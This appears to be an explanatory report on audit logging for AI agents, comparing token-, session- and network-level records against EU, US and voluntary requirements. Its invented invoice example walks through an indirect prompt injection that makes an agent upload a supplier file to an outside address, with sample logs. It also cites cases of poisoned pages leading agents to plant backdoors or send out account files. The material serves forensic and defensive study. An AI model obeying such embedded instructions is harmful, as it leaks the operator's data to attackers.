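# Audit logs for AI agents: token-level, session-level and combined network and model records compared

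## What an AI agent does that can be logged, and the three kinds of log

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop, so that the model can call tools and act on other systems as well as write text. This software, called the harness, assembles the model's input, executes its tool calls (such as a search, a file write or a web request) and returns the results to the model. An audit log is a record, made while the agent works, from which someone else can later establish what it did. Security staff use these logs to reconstruct incidents, and some laws and standards require them.

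How much a log can show depends on where in the agent's work it is recorded. The same action can appear as a few hundred tokens (the units of text a model reads and writes, averaging about four characters of English), as one line in a list of events, or as a connection from one machine to another.

### The agent loop and who can record it

A session is one agent run, from its first instruction to its end. Four parties can record parts of it: the provider that runs the model, the operator of the harness, the operator of the machines and network the agent uses, and the service the agent acts on, such as a mail server or an ordering system. One company may fill several of these roles. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the loop for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, and Anthropic documents a nearly identical one for agents that run on its Claude models.

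The harness first assembles a request. In Codex, the request contains standing instructions, tool definitions, a note on file permissions and network access, a description of the working directory, and the user's message. The harness operator can record all of this word for word, but the model receives slightly different text because OpenAI's server turns the request into the final prompt. The server sets the order of the opening items and controls the content of the system message, which has the highest priority.

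The next step is the model call, which is one request to the model and the output it returns. The server converts the text into tokens, which are integers that index the model's vocabulary. The model produces new tokens one at a time, and the server converts them back into text. Customers normally send and receive text, so the provider is best placed to record the exact tokens. A company that runs an openly released model on its own machines is its own provider and can record them too.

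Access to the model's reasoning is split in a similar way. Many models write a chain of thought, the reasoning text that precedes an answer or action. Codex receives it as a readable summary plus an encrypted block, which the harness stores and sends back with the next request but cannot read. Gruber and Hilgert (2026), in *Foundations for Investigations of Agentic AI Systems*, found the same limit when they examined the files that OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, leaves on disk. OpenClaw saves whatever reasoning the provider returns. For current flagship models such as Claude and Gemini, the files held summaries and encrypted signatures, although the summaries from one smaller model, Gemini 2.5 Flash, were informative.

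The model's output is either a final reply or a tool call, which is a request for the harness to execute an action. A tool call carries a tool name, arguments and an identifier that links it to its result. Before executing the call, the harness may check a rule, run a hook (the operator's own code, which runs at a fixed point in the loop) or prompt a person to decide. The harness operator is best placed to record that decision. In Anthropic's toolkit, the model receives a rejection message when the harness denies a call. The harness never executes a denied call, so the network operator and the outside service have nothing to record. The denied call still appears in the harness's own record and in the text of the model calls, where the model's output contains the request and its next input contains the rejection.

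If the harness does execute a shell command, the command may start other programs, open files and connect to other machines, but the harness may log only the command and its final output. The operator of the machine and network can record the other activity from outside the harness. A service that receives a request has its own record of the request as it arrived, the account that made it and whatever changed as a result. An investigator usually has to ask another organisation for that record, but the agent's operator cannot have edited it. Some tools, such as OpenAI's web search, run on the provider's side, so their traffic never crosses the operator's network.

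The harness then appends the result to the input and calls the model again, so each request includes everything in the previous one. Codex could refer the server to an earlier response instead, but Bolin explains that it resends everything so that each request is self-contained. This also suits customers whose contracts forbid OpenAI to retain their data. OpenAI processes the full text of their calls but keeps none of it, so the operator has to make any lasting record.

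A model can take in only so much text at once. When the input nears that limit in a long session, the harness compacts it by replacing older messages with a summary. Anthropic's toolkit emits a marker when this happens and offers a hook that can archive the full transcript beforehand. According to its documentation, specific instructions from early in the conversation may not survive. After compaction, a complete record of the session no longer matches the text the model receives.

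Splitting records among these parties causes trouble in practice. *Tracing the Messy Middle* (Hou, Li and colleagues, 2026) compares the two records a company is most likely to have of its coding agents: the log of a gateway, a proxy through which model calls pass, and the transcripts the agents write to disk. Over 93 days, the transcripts held 6,775 requests and the gateway log held 91, because the other 6,684 ran under subscription logins that bypassed the gateway. In a separate controlled trace of 60 requests, the gateway routed every request to MiniMax-M2.7, but the transcript listed claude-sonnet-4-6, the model the agent was set to address. This was one small deployment, and Hou and colleagues present it as proof that such gaps exist, not as an estimate of how common they are.

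### Three levels of log

A token-level log records the exact sequence of tokens the model read and wrote in each call, along with settings such as the model version and the sampling temperature (which controls how random the choice of each token is). It is the closest available record of what entered and left the model. It shows what happened after a tool call only through the text that the harness later fed back to the model.

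A session-level log records a session as ordered events: prompts, replies, tool calls, results and approvals, with or without their content. *Agentic process evidence* (Kainan and Hershman, 2026) proposes a format with one log file per session. It requires only a session identifier, the name and version of the harness, and a timeline of at least one event, each with its own identifier, kind and time. The timeline records prompts, chain of thought, replies, and tool calls with their arguments and results. The model's name is optional, but the format has separate fields for the model requested and the model actually used, a distinction that Hou and colleagues found blurred.

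A network-plus-model log combines network and host records made outside the agent with records of the model calls that caused the traffic. The link between them may be a correlation identifier (a value carried through model calls, tool calls and network requests) or weaker evidence such as time and process. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) illustrates why the records need combining with the case of a poisoned web page that leads a coding agent to plant a backdoor. A monitor inside the application records a successful "execute script" call, and a monitor on the operating system records a shell process writing to a file, but neither record alone distinguishes the attack from ordinary work.

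These three names are working definitions, since the field has no settled vocabulary. Wang, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents*, a survey of 90 studies, sort logging by the place where it happens:

- Execution-level logging ties together the events of a whole run or workflow.
- Invocation-level logging captures individual calls to models or tools.
- Communication-level logging captures exchanges across the boundaries between agents or system components, such as messages between agents, handoffs of a task and protocol exchanges.

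A session-level log corresponds to execution-level logging, and most of its entries are invocation-level records. A token-level log is invocation-level logging of model calls, but the survey has no separate term for logging at that level of detail. The network-plus-model log fits the survey's categories least well. Its traffic records resemble communication-level logging, but that category also includes messages between two agents on the same machine. A network-plus-model log differs from the other two because part of it is captured from outside the agent, which the survey treats as a question of method. It calls capture from outside "boundary interception" and capture by code within the agent's software "integrated instrumentation". Most of the logging systems Wang and colleagues reviewed use instrumentation, and only a few combine it with observation from outside.

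### An invented example: the invoice agent

The following session is invented, and its round numbers are there to make the arithmetic easy. A company's agent reconciles supplier invoices against payment records. It makes 60 model calls, each followed by one tool call, and the last tool call files the finished reconciliation. The session starts with 5,000 tokens of input: instructions, tool definitions and the task. Each model call then adds 2,000 tokens, of which the model writes 500 and the tool returns 1,500. No compaction takes place. The session therefore holds

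5,000 + 60 × 2,000 = 125,000 distinct tokens.

The harness re-sends the whole history with each call, so the input to call *n* is 5,000 + (*n* − 1) × 2,000 tokens, or 85,000 at call 41 and 123,000 at call 60. Over the session, the model reads 3.84 million tokens of input, about 31 times the number of distinct tokens. This difference affects the cost of storage.

In call 41, the model reads for the first time the invoice that the previous tool call returned. The invoice contains a hidden instruction, perhaps in white text on a white page, to send the company's supplier list to an outside address for "verification". The model responds with a tool call that uploads the list. Security researchers call this an indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker places instructions in material that the agent will read as part of its work.

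A token-level log records the event as a sequence of numbered tokens. The invoice occupies positions 83,501 to 85,000 of the input, and the model's output comes immediately after it.

```
call 41   model M, version 2026-08   temperature 1.0
read 1-85,000   wrote 85,001-85,500
position 84,310   token  4128   " send"
position 84,311   token   279   " the"
position 84,312   token 20972   " supplier"
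position 84,313   token  1160   " list"
...
position 85,471   token  1277   "http"
position 85,472   token  6226   "_post"
```

The session-level log has five entries for the same seconds.

```
10:42:07   tool result   t40   read_invoice: "Invoice 8841 ..."
10:42:15   reasoning           summary: "Supplier list requested. Sending it."
10:42:15   tool call     t41   http_post, file suppliers.csv,
                               to verify-suppliers.example
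10:42:15   permission    t41   allowed by rule, no person asked
10:42:16   tool result   t41   status 200 (success)
```

The network-plus-model log starts from the end of the model call and follows the process that acted on it.

```
10:42:15.210   model call 41 ends        session inv-0925, process 3120
10:42:15.304   process 3120 reads file   suppliers.csv
10:42:15.377   process 3120 connects     203.0.113.7, port 443
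10:42:15.902   connection closes         48,212 bytes out, 310 bytes in
match          call 41                   same process, 167 ms after reply
```

None of these logs contains the supplier list. The harness uploaded the file straight from disk, so its contents never passed through the model as tokens. The session-level log has the file's name, and the network-plus-model log has only its approximate size, because the connection was encrypted. To learn which suppliers' details leaked, an investigator would need a copy of the file as it stood at 10:42 that morning.

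Zheng and colleagues staged a real attack similar to this one. They told a coding agent to build a program whose instructions pointed to a web page with a hidden prompt, and the agent read a system file of user accounts and sent it to a collection server. Their monitoring tool recorded everything from the first page load to the outgoing transfer as 521 events, which it merged into 37. This is a single case study, but it shows that both kinds of record can be combined in one account.

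### What an investigator needs to know

Lists of what an agent's records should show overlap a good deal. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (Tallam, 2026) covers who acted, under what authority, on which resources, under what policy and with what outcome. Gruber and Hilgert organise a forensic examination around how the agent was configured, what it knew, whom it communicated with, what it did and whether anyone had asked for it. TechTarget's *What CISOs need to know about AI audit logs*, a checklist for chief information security officers, also includes the model's version and reasoning. For the invoice agent, these lists can be reduced to six questions.

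| Question | Token-level log | Session-level log | Network-plus-model log |
|---|---|---|---|
| What happened? | Only what the model asked for and what the harness told it | Yes, as the harness reported it | Yes, for files, processes and connections |
| In what order? | Yes, for model calls | Yes | Yes, by a clock outside the agent |
| On whose authority? | No, beyond claims in the text | Yes, if it holds identities and approvals | In part: the process and account used |
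| What had the model read? | Yes, exactly | In part | Only if it keeps the content of model calls |
| Why did it act? | In part: the fullest reasoning text | In part: the reasoning the provider released | No |
| What left the network? | No, beyond the tool call's arguments | In part: the request and the reported result | Yes: destination, time and size, but content only with decryption |

A session-level log is the most convenient source for what happened and in what order, but its reliability depends on whether the software that writes it records events accurately. Gruber and Hilgert note that a tool call present in OpenClaw's runtime logs but missing from the session transcript can point to tampering. Kainan and Hershman cite a review of the July 2026 breach of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, by OpenAI's agents. The investigators found spoofed tool calls in some transcripts.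 Investigators can check a transcript against a record made outside the agent.

It is harder to recover who authorized an action than the table suggests. Suppose a clerk started the invoice session, and an administrator had written the rule that let the agent send web requests without asking. Tallam argues that a record naming only the last actor is not enough, because responsibility extends along the chain of people and programs that passed on the permission. Few logs record that chain. Wang and colleagues found that agent logs commonly include inputs, outputs and timing, while fewer systems record permissions and reasoning.

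A session-level log may look complete but omit some of what the model read. The OpenClaw transcripts were the richest source Gruber and Hilgert found, since they hold messages, reasoning and tool calls together. But OpenClaw does not store the full input it assembled for each call, which also drew on memory files and settings that may have changed since. For the invoice agent, the gap would be small, because the session-level log quotes the tool result containing the malicious text. If the operator had kept only names and sizes, the log would show that the agent opened invoice 8841 and then uploaded a file, but not how the two were connected.

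No log fully shows why the agent acted. A chain of thought is imperfect evidence of the model's reasons, and many operators receive only a summary of it. Gruber and Hilgert add that identical inputs can produce different behaviour, so even a perfect reconstruction of the input leaves more than one possible explanation. A stronger test is to change the suspected cause and run the step again, and Wang and colleagues describe methods that do this. A token-level log is well suited to this test because an investigator can delete the hidden instruction from the input to call 41, repeat the call many times and count how often the model still sends the list.

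A bigger log is therefore not always better. Wang and colleagues conclude that whether evidence is sufficient depends on the question, and that later analysis cannot faithfully recover what nobody recorded at the time. *An Evidence Model for Agentic Processes* (2026) recommends asking which property each record supports, by what mechanism, under which assumptions about whom to trust, and against which threat. The 48,212 bytes recorded in the network-plus-model log support the claim that a transfer of that size took place, provided one trusts the machine's operator, but do not show that the model meant to leak anything.

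### Debugging logs and audit records

Many agents already write logs, but mostly to help developers fix bugs. Tallam distinguishes these debugging logs from audit records. Programmers choose what to put in a debugging log, and nothing guarantees that it is complete. Audit records follow a fixed structure, cover every decision and are tamper-evident, meaning that anyone can detect a later change or deletion. An auditor should also be able to work from part of the records and tell a missing entry from an action that never took place. Common practice falls short of this. According to *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026), most agents keep a simple log file that a malicious tool can overwrite. The version of OpenClaw that Gruber and Hilgert examined deletes its runtime logs after 24 hours. Signing the records helps, but Kainan and Hershman caution that a valid signature proves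 only who produced a record and that nobody has altered it since, not that the record is complete or true.

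## What laws and standards ask the records to show

Record-keeping laws usually state a purpose, such as spotting risks or preserving what a firm told its customers, and rarely specify a level of logging. Companies have to work out how much detail the purpose requires. For example, the logging articles of the EU AI Act, the broadest of these laws, do not mention tokens or a model's reasoning. A session-level log with the right fields meets most of the duties that now apply to AI agents.

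### Article 12: what a system must record

The AI Act's logging duties apply to high-risk AI systems. A system is usually high-risk because it serves a use listed in Annex III, such as remote biometric identification or screening job applicants, or because it is part of a regulated product under Annex I, such as a medical device. Many office agents belong to neither group. The invoice agent reconciles payments between companies, which is not an Annex III use, so these duties would not require its operator to keep a log. They normally would apply if the company built a similar agent to rank job applicants.

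The Act requires a system's provider to build logging into it. According to the definitions in artificialintelligenceact.eu's *Article 12*, the provider is the firm that develops a system, or has it developed, and puts it on the market or into service under its own name. This system provider is often a different company from the one that runs the model. For example, a software company that builds a recruitment agent around a model that another company runs is the system provider, and an employer that uses the agent is the deployer. An employer that builds an agent for its own recruiters is both provider and deployer.

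The text in the European Commission's *Article 12* requires high-risk systems to "technically allow for the automatic recording of events (logs)" throughout their lifetime. The logs must cover events relevant to three purposes:

- identifying situations in which the system may present a risk, or may have changed substantially since its assessment
- helping the system provider monitor the system after sale
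- helping the deployer monitor the system in use

Article 12 of the EU AI Act sets minimum log contents only for remote biometric identification, which means recognising people at a distance. Those systems must record when each use started and ended, the reference database, the input that led to a match, and the people who verified the result. For every other high-risk system, the Act requires a level of traceability "appropriate to the intended purpose".

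Article 12 also does not define "events". If the invoice session came under the Act, its operator could count the whole run as one event, or count each of the 60 model calls and 60 tool calls, for a total of 120 plus the permission decisions. The article does not specify whether an entry must include the text of a prompt or only its time and size. It does not require network records or tamper-evidence.

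The three purposes rule out the most basic logs. A line stating that the invoice agent ran from 10:00 to 10:50 would not help anyone identify a risk. A metadata-only log would show an upload to an unfamiliar address, which might be enough to raise an alarm, but it would not show what prompted the upload. It is debatable whether "identifying situations" includes finding their cause.

Engineers and researchers have proposed quite different answers. *Record-Keeping*, an engineering guide from the appliedAI Institute, uses an inference log with metadata for all three purposes: finding inputs that cause unwanted behaviour, detecting gradual changes in the data or the system's performance, and monitoring operation. This approach suits an agent less well than a system that makes one prediction per input, because an agent may cause harm through a series of steps that each look ordinary.

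*EU AI Act Article 12 and the Interaction-Trace Gap*, a paper on high-risk work that people and AI systems do together, argues that a log of inputs, outputs, times, tool calls, model versions and errors is not enough to comply. Many serious failures in such work come from unclear roles, poor delegation or weak oversight. For example, a log might show that a recruiter approved a rejection but not whether the recruiter had seen the application. The paper is an academic reading of the Act and is not legally binding, but its point about oversight is fair, because an approval is poor evidence of review if nobody knows what the reviewer saw. The extra records it calls for would still belong in a session-level log, since exact tokens would not show who was responsible for a decision.

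The least detailed log that would safely satisfy Article 12 for an agent is a session-level log of model calls, tool calls and approvals, with times, versions and outcomes. It should also hold enough content, or a reliable pointer to that content, to trace a harmful action back to its input. A metadata-only log may satisfy the wording of Article 12 for a simple system with few ways to cause harm.

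### Articles 19 and 26(6): who must keep the logs

Article 12 concerns what a system is able to record, while Articles 19 and 26 require providers and deployers to keep the logs. Article 19, as reproduced by activeMind.legal, requires providers to keep the automatically generated logs they control for a period appropriate to the system's purpose, and for at least six months. Paragraph 6 of the European Commission's *Article 26* sets a matching duty for deployers. Banks and other financial institutions with documentation duties under EU financial services law keep the logs as part of that documentation.

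Under both articles, the six-month minimum applies unless other EU or national law, particularly data-protection law, provides otherwise. Six months can also be too short. If rejected applicants have a year to challenge a decision, keeping a recruitment agent's logs for only six months would hardly be "appropriate" to its purpose. Default settings may keep logs for much less than the minimum. OpenClaw, for example, limits runtime logs to 24 hours, so a high-risk system that relied on those files as its Article 12 logs would need different settings.

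The words "under their control" matter more for agents than for most software, because several companies hold parts of the record. An employer that rents a recruitment agent as a web service may control only the decisions it exports, and Article 26(6) does not require it to obtain the remaining logs from the seller. Neither article covers the exact tokens held by a model company, unless that company is also the provider or deployer of the high-risk system. An employer that expects to need those records has to arrange access by contract.

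A deployer that stores logs for six months and never looks at them would meet Article 26(6) but could easily breach Article 26(5), which requires deployers to monitor the system according to its instructions. If they have reason to think that using it as instructed may present a risk, they must suspend its use and inform the seller and the authorities without undue delay. After a serious incident, they must immediately inform the system provider, and then the importer or distributor and the authorities.

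### Application dates after the 2026 Omnibus

These duties do not apply yet because the European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744 of the European Parliament and of the Council* (2026), known as the Digital Omnibus on AI, postponed them. The Future of Privacy Forum (2026) dates its publication to 24 July 2026 and its entry into force to 27 July. Under the new Article 113, the sections of the Act containing Articles 12, 19 and 26 apply from 2 December 2027 to high-risk systems under Annex III, and from 2 August 2028 to those under Annex I.

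The Act applies to a high-risk system already on the market before the relevant date only if its design changes significantly afterwards. Providers and deployers of systems intended for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030 even without such a change. An agent's operator may replace the model, add tools or rewrite the instructions several times a year, so whether the Act applies will depend largely on which changes count as significant. An operator that wants to rely on the exemption should record those changes with their dates.

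The Omnibus also lets the AI Office, the Commission's supervisory body for AI, order operators under its direct supervision to retain all data and documents it considers necessary to assess compliance. The Office generally has five years from an infringement to impose a penalty. Suppose such an operator runs a high-risk session on 10 January 2028 and deletes the log on 10 July, as soon as the minimum retention period ends. The Office could still penalise an infringement from that session until January 2033, and the operator would no longer have the log to use in its defence.

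The Omnibus names agentic AI in a list of codes for the technologies that a conformity assessment body is competent to assess, but the code does not change Article 12. The Commission is also to issue guidelines on Articles 8 to 15, 25 and 26, which include the recording duty and the deployer's retention duty. These guidelines may be of more practical help.

### ISO/IEC 24970 and its European counterpart

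One reason the EU gave for the delay was that technical standards were late. Two of them deal with logging. ISO/IEC 24970 is an international standard on AI system logging, and prEN 18229-1 is a European draft meant to connect logging practice to the Act. Smith (2026) explains in *Two standards, one architecture* that the international standard supplies the technical foundation, while the European one provides the mapping that gives a company a presumption of conformity. This means that a company following the standard counts as meeting the matching legal requirement unless someone shows otherwise.

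ISO/IEC's *Artificial intelligence — AI system logging* (2025), the draft of the international standard, was open for voting from 18 November 2025 to 10 February 2026. Smith reported that it had reached the final-draft stage by 5 June and that neither standard was finished. An undated project entry from the German standards institute, DIN's *Artificial intelligence*, refers to "ISO/IEC 24970:2026", which suggests that the international standard has been published or soon will be, but the entry still lists the European version as a final draft. The European draft, CEN's *AI trustworthiness framework* (2026), is further behind. It entered its public enquiry on 28 May 2026, more than 15 months after its due date. Its catalogue entry marks it as not harmonised under the AI Act, so it creates no presumption of conformity.

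VDE's *EU AI Act* (2025), a clause-by-clause summary by the German electrotechnical association, gives the clearest outline of the draft's contents. Under the draft, routine operation, automated monitoring and human oversight each trigger logging. Entries must include error codes and messages, severity, the operation that failed, and any retries, fallbacks or escalation. They also carry times, component identifiers and, where privacy permits, user identifiers. The draft prescribes no fixed schema but includes a sample data structure. It reserves long-term storage for records that a law or regulation requires, and a governance scheme defines who may read, write or delete them.

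VDE's outline does not require logs to include prompts, tokens or chain of thought. Its emphasis on errors also fits prompt injection poorly. In the invoice session, call 41 produced no error, so a log that covered only failures would contain nothing about the theft. The trigger for routine operation would capture the upload if the system's designers had classed successful tool calls as events worth recording. A session-level log can meet the draft's requirements, but how useful it is for agents depends on that choice.

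### NIST and the identity of agents

The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) writes standards and guidance that private companies mostly follow voluntarily. Its work on agents is at an earlier stage. In February 2026 its cybersecurity centre published a concept paper on identity and authorization for software and AI agents, which invited comments on how to log an agent's actions verifiably and tie them to a human authorization. The paper outlines a possible project and sets no requirements. NIST has also requested information on the security of agents. Bengio, Kankanhalli and colleagues (2026) note in the Singapore Consensus, an international report on AI safety research, that this request treats threats among several agents as a separate area of risk. They expect NIST's planned reports on security controls for AI to take the same approach.

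An audit needs to establish whose authority an agent used, and an account name may not show this. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 89 sources and found few documented deployments in which people could reliably trace an agent's consequential actions to a person, limit them to what that person had delegated, and contest them afterwards. The paper proposes describing each tool call by seven elements: the chain of people and programs behind it, the operation, its target, its arguments, the scope of the delegation, the time and session, and evidence of where the content behind the call came from.

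For call 41, the chain runs from the clerk who started the session to the agent, under a permission that an administrator had set. The operation was a web upload, the target was the outside address, and the argument was the supplier file. The clerk had delegated invoice reconciliation, which did not include sending out supplier lists. The instruction to upload the file came from invoice 8841, and an invoice is not an authorized source of instructions. The agent had technical permission for the call, so the session-level log accurately shows "allowed by rule". An auditor needs the delegated scope and the origin of the instruction to see why the rule should not have allowed the call.

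Some of this evidence can be sent with a request. Bengio and colleagues report that OpenAI's ChatGPT agent cryptographically signs its outgoing web requests so that the receiving service can verify their source. They also describe "on-behalf-of" credentials, which identify both the agent and the user who delegated the task. An investigator could then find the same identity in the operator's session-level log and in the outside service's records. A valid signature does not prove that the user wanted the agent to make the request.

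### Broker-dealer and health-data rules

Older industry-specific rules already cover some agents, because they apply to a business's records whether a person or a program wrote them. Two American examples show how much the required detail can vary.

Securities and Exchange Commission Rule 17a-4 requires broker-dealers, the firms that trade securities for clients or themselves, to preserve the communications they send and receive about their business for at least three years, the first two in an easily accessible place. They must keep some core accounting records for six years. If an agent emails a client about a trade, the firm has to keep the full message. A log of metadata alone would not be enough, because it would record that the agent sent an email but not what the email said. The firm does not need to keep the tokens from which the model built the message. It is less clear whether an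 employee's instructions to an agent count as business communications, so a cautious firm would keep those too.

The rule also says that firms must keep electronic records either in storage that nobody can rewrite or erase, or in a system with a complete, time-stamped audit trail of changes and deletions that lets the firm recreate the original. This goes further than Article 12 of the AI Act, which requires automatic recording but no protection against later edits. An ordinary session transcript on the agent's own disk would meet neither option, because the agent or its operator could overwrite it without trace.

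The Security Rule under HIPAA, the US health-privacy law, applies to most healthcare providers, health insurers and the contractors that handle electronic patient data for them. Its audit-control standard, section 164.312(b), requires mechanisms that record and examine activity in systems containing such data, but it doesn't list which fields to record. For an agent that looks up patient records, it could be enough to log the account, the patient file, the action and the time, without prompts or replies. Host and database logs could supply much of this information. The agent should have its own account, because a shared login would hide whether a nurse or the agent had opened a file.

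HIPAA requires organisations to keep their security documentation for six years, but section 164.312(b) sets no retention period for audit logs, and lawyers disagree on whether the six-year rule covers them. Many organisations keep the logs for six years to be safe. They can keep only the access log for that long, and not the session text, which would contain far more patient information.

### State laws on frontier developers

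California and New York regulate the companies that develop the most powerful models. California's SB 53, in force since January 2026, requires large developers to publish a safety framework and to report critical safety incidents to the state, generally within 15 days of discovering them. New York's RAISE Act, signed in December 2025, requires developers to publish safety plans and report incidents within 72 hours. Neither law specifies how detailed an agent's logs must be or requires developers to keep a record of each agent session.

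Both laws depend on such records indirectly. A developer cannot report an incident it never noticed, and it will struggle to describe one accurately without some account of what the agent did. But the developer still chooses the evidence, so in a dispute the state might have a timely report and no underlying log to check it against.

### The Singapore Consensus and reasoning traces

The 2026 Singapore Consensus and its companion report on agents give the fullest description of what to record, but they are voluntary. More than 100 contributors from 13 countries worked on the Consensus, which followed a meeting of researchers, companies and government institutes in May. Bengio and colleagues describe it as "not a policy document". The companion report sets out ten principles. The third, auditability, is that authorized parties should be able to reconstruct and verify an agent's decisions and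 actions during a session and afterwards.

Under the principle, developers should build logging that captures inputs, tool calls with their parameters, outputs, outcomes and reasoning traces. These traces include how the agent broke down its goal, which plans it rejected, and how retrieved information influenced its decisions. Developers should also let users inspect what the agent did for them. Deployers should protect the logs, make them tamper-evident and set up alerts. Where several agents work together, whoever runs the coordinating software should keep the records coherent across organisations.

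Much of this exceeds the legal minimum. For call 41, an operator could argue that Article 12 requires only the time, the tool, the destination and the result. The Singapore principle would add the text of the invoice, the upload's parameters and the reasoning that connected them. These additions would make the log far more useful to an investigator, who could see the malicious instruction alongside the agent's response.

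The call for reasoning traces is harder to meet. A developer can record tool calls directly, but it can learn about rejected plans only from what the model wrote down, and the model company may release only a summary of that. In the invoice session, the summary was "Supplier list requested. Sending it." This omits the most important fact, which is who requested the list. According to the companion report, Google's approach is more modest and captures intermediate reasoning "where feasible".

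Bengio and colleagues also claim that regulators and standards bodies are converging on audit trails that are automatic, tamper-evident and complete enough to reconstruct a system's decisions. Their examples only partly support this. A Chinese framework requires operators to log system and user activity, and China's national cyber-response centre recommends a complete log-audit mechanism for OpenClaw. Article 12, which the report calls the most explicit example, requires automatic recording but not tamper-evidence or the reconstruction of every decision. IBM's proposal to anchor each agent action in a cryptographic chain of evidence is an industry design idea that none of the laws above adopts.

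Even the Singapore principle does not require a token-level log, because a session-level log can hold the inputs, actions and reasoning as readable text if the model company releases them. The table shows which of the three levels each duty requires. A level counts as necessary only where a less detailed log would not satisfy the duty.

| Duty | Token-level log | Session-level log | Network-plus-model log | Retention and date |
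|---|---|---|---|---|
| AI Act, Article 12 | Not required | Sufficient, if it can link harmful actions to inputs | Not required, but can help detect risks | Applies from 2 December 2027 (Annex III) or 2 August 2028 (Annex I) |
| AI Act, Articles 19 and 26(6) | Keep if the system generates it automatically and the firm controls it | Same rule | Same rule | At least six months, subject to other law; same dates |
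| ISO/IEC 24970, draft | Not in VDE's outline | Sufficient, if it covers successful actions as well as errors | Not in VDE's outline | Long-term storage only where a law or regulation requires it |
| SEC Rule 17a-4 | Not required | Must hold the full text of business communications | Not required | Three years for communications, six for some other records; in force |
| HIPAA audit controls | Not required | Metadata can be sufficient | Host and database records can serve instead | No stated period for audit logs; in force |
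| California SB 53 and New York RAISE Act | Not required | Not required, though incident reports depend on some record | Not required | Incident reports within 15 days (California) or 72 hours (New York) |
| Singapore Consensus, auditability | Not required | Needs content, actions, outcomes and available reasoning | Not required | Voluntary; no period |

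## Recording every token the model reads and writes

None of the laws and standards above requires a token-level log. An operator might still keep one because it supports tests that other records do not. An investigator can rerun a recorded model call, check whether the output came from the stated model, and remove a suspected cause to see whether the action still follows. These tests need specific log fields, some of which customers of the main commercial models cannot get.

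### The fields of a complete record

For call 41 of the invoice session, a complete record would look like this. The probabilities are invented, like the rest of the example.

| Field | In call 41 | What it adds to readable text |
|---|---|---|
| Assembled input | 85,000 tokens, in the order the model read them | The exact position of every instruction and tool result |
| Token identifiers | 4128 for " send", 279 for " the" | Invisible characters, and the difference between a real control marker and an imitation |
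| Output tokens | Positions 85,001 to 85,500 | The full chain of thought, where a transcript may have a summary or nothing |
| Model and tokenizer version | Model M, version 2026-08 | Which model to load for a rerun, and what the identifiers stand for |
| Sampling settings | Temperature 1.0, cut-offs, random seed | How the software chose each token |
| Probabilities of alternatives (optional) | " send" 55%, " skip" 45% at one point in the reasoning | How close the model came to writing something else |
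| Time of each token (optional) | Last token at 10:42:15.210 | A precise point to match against network records |
| Serving conditions (optional) | Processor type, software version, batch size | What to hold constant for an exact repeat |

In the assembled input, special tokens mark where the system message ends and where each user message or tool result begins. A transcript usually replaces them with plain labels. Suppose an injection hidden in invoice 8841 imitated the marker that opens a user's turn. The transcript would look the same whether the server had converted the imitation into ordinary characters or into the real marker. If the server had produced the real marker, the model would have received the attacker's words as if the clerk had typed them. The token identifiers would show which conversion happened because the real marker has its own number.

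An investigator cannot always recover the token identifiers from the text, because several token sequences can spell the same words. The model may respond differently to each sequence.

The sampling settings explain how the software turned the model's calculations into a choice. At each position, the model gives every token in its vocabulary a score, called a logit. Two cut-offs, top-k and top-p, may exclude unlikely tokens. Karvonen, Reuter and colleagues (2025), in *DiFR*, describe the method that most current serving software then uses. For each remaining token, it computes

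ℓ + *T* × *g*,

where ℓ is the logit, *T* is the temperature and *g* is a random number determined by the seed. The token with the largest total wins. Anyone who has the logits, temperature and seed can therefore work out the choice again. At temperature zero the random term disappears and the model always takes the highest-scoring token, a setting known as greedy decoding.

Recorded probabilities show what else the model might have written. If " send" had a 55% chance and " skip" had 45%, the model was almost as likely to skip the upload as to make it, but the transcript would show only that it chose to send the list. *Beyond Reproducibility* (2026) uses these probabilities to compare repeated runs, because they reveal small differences even when the chosen token stays the same. Recording probabilities also makes the log larger, so an operator might keep them only for the few most likely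 tokens at each position.

### Who can make the record

Operators of open-weight models, whose trained parameters anyone can download, can keep every field in the table, and so can providers of hosted models. The largest gap in the logs of a provider's customers is the model's reasoning.

Anthropic's *Thinking*, the documentation for reasoning on its Claude models, states that no display setting returns the raw chain of thought. A customer can ask for a summary, which a different model writes, but on most recent Claude models the default is an empty field. Only the encrypted signature contains the full reasoning. In *The text in Claude Code's "Extended Thinking" output is not authentic*, McCanna describes opening the session files that Anthropic's coding agent had saved on his machine and finding a 600-character signature and no reasoning text.

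According to AWS's *Differences in thinking across model versions*, Claude 3.7 Sonnet returned its full reasoning, whereas the later Claude 4 models return a summary.

OpenAI's arrangement is similar. Customers get a count of the reasoning tokens as well as the summary and encrypted block that Codex receives, according to OpenAI's *Reasoning models*, a guide that covers models up to GPT-5.5. In the guide's sample response, 1,024 of 1,186 output tokens are reasoning, so a customer's log would lack about 86% of what the model wrote. OpenAI's *How to handle the raw chain of thought in gpt-oss* explains how software that serves the company's open-weight models can return the raw reasoning, and adds that its hosted models will not offer this for now. According to Google's *Gemini thinking*, the summary that accompanies a Gemini model's signature may be empty.

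Operators should keep the encrypted blocks anyway. A stored signature is an encrypted copy of the reasoning behind call 41, and Anthropic's servers can decrypt it. An investigator would need Anthropic's cooperation to read it, but if the operator has discarded the block, there may be nothing left to decrypt. Anthropic may have its own copy, but it may delete that copy on a schedule the operator does not control.

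Hosted services also limit the sampling settings. Requests to recent Claude models fail if they set temperature, top-k or top-p to a non-default value, so customers cannot switch to greedy decoding to make a replay more predictable.

### Replaying a recorded call

To replay call 41, an investigator with access to the weights would take these steps:

1. Load version 2026-08 of model M and its tokenizer, with the same numerical precision and, if possible, the same kind of processor.
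2. Feed in the 85,000 recorded token identifiers, without converting them to text and back.
3. Set the recorded temperature, cut-offs and seed.
4. Generate up to 500 tokens and compare each one with the record.

If all 500 match, the investigator has strong evidence that the record is accurate. The record may still be accurate if some don't match, because identical settings can produce different outputs.

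This happens because computers round the result of each addition, so the order in which numbers are added can change the total. Thinking Machines Lab's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* gives an extreme example. Adding 0.1 to 10²⁰ and then subtracting 10²⁰ gives 0, because the 0.1 is lost to rounding. Subtracting 10²⁰ from itself first and then adding 0.1 gives 0.1. A language model performs a huge number of these additions for each token.

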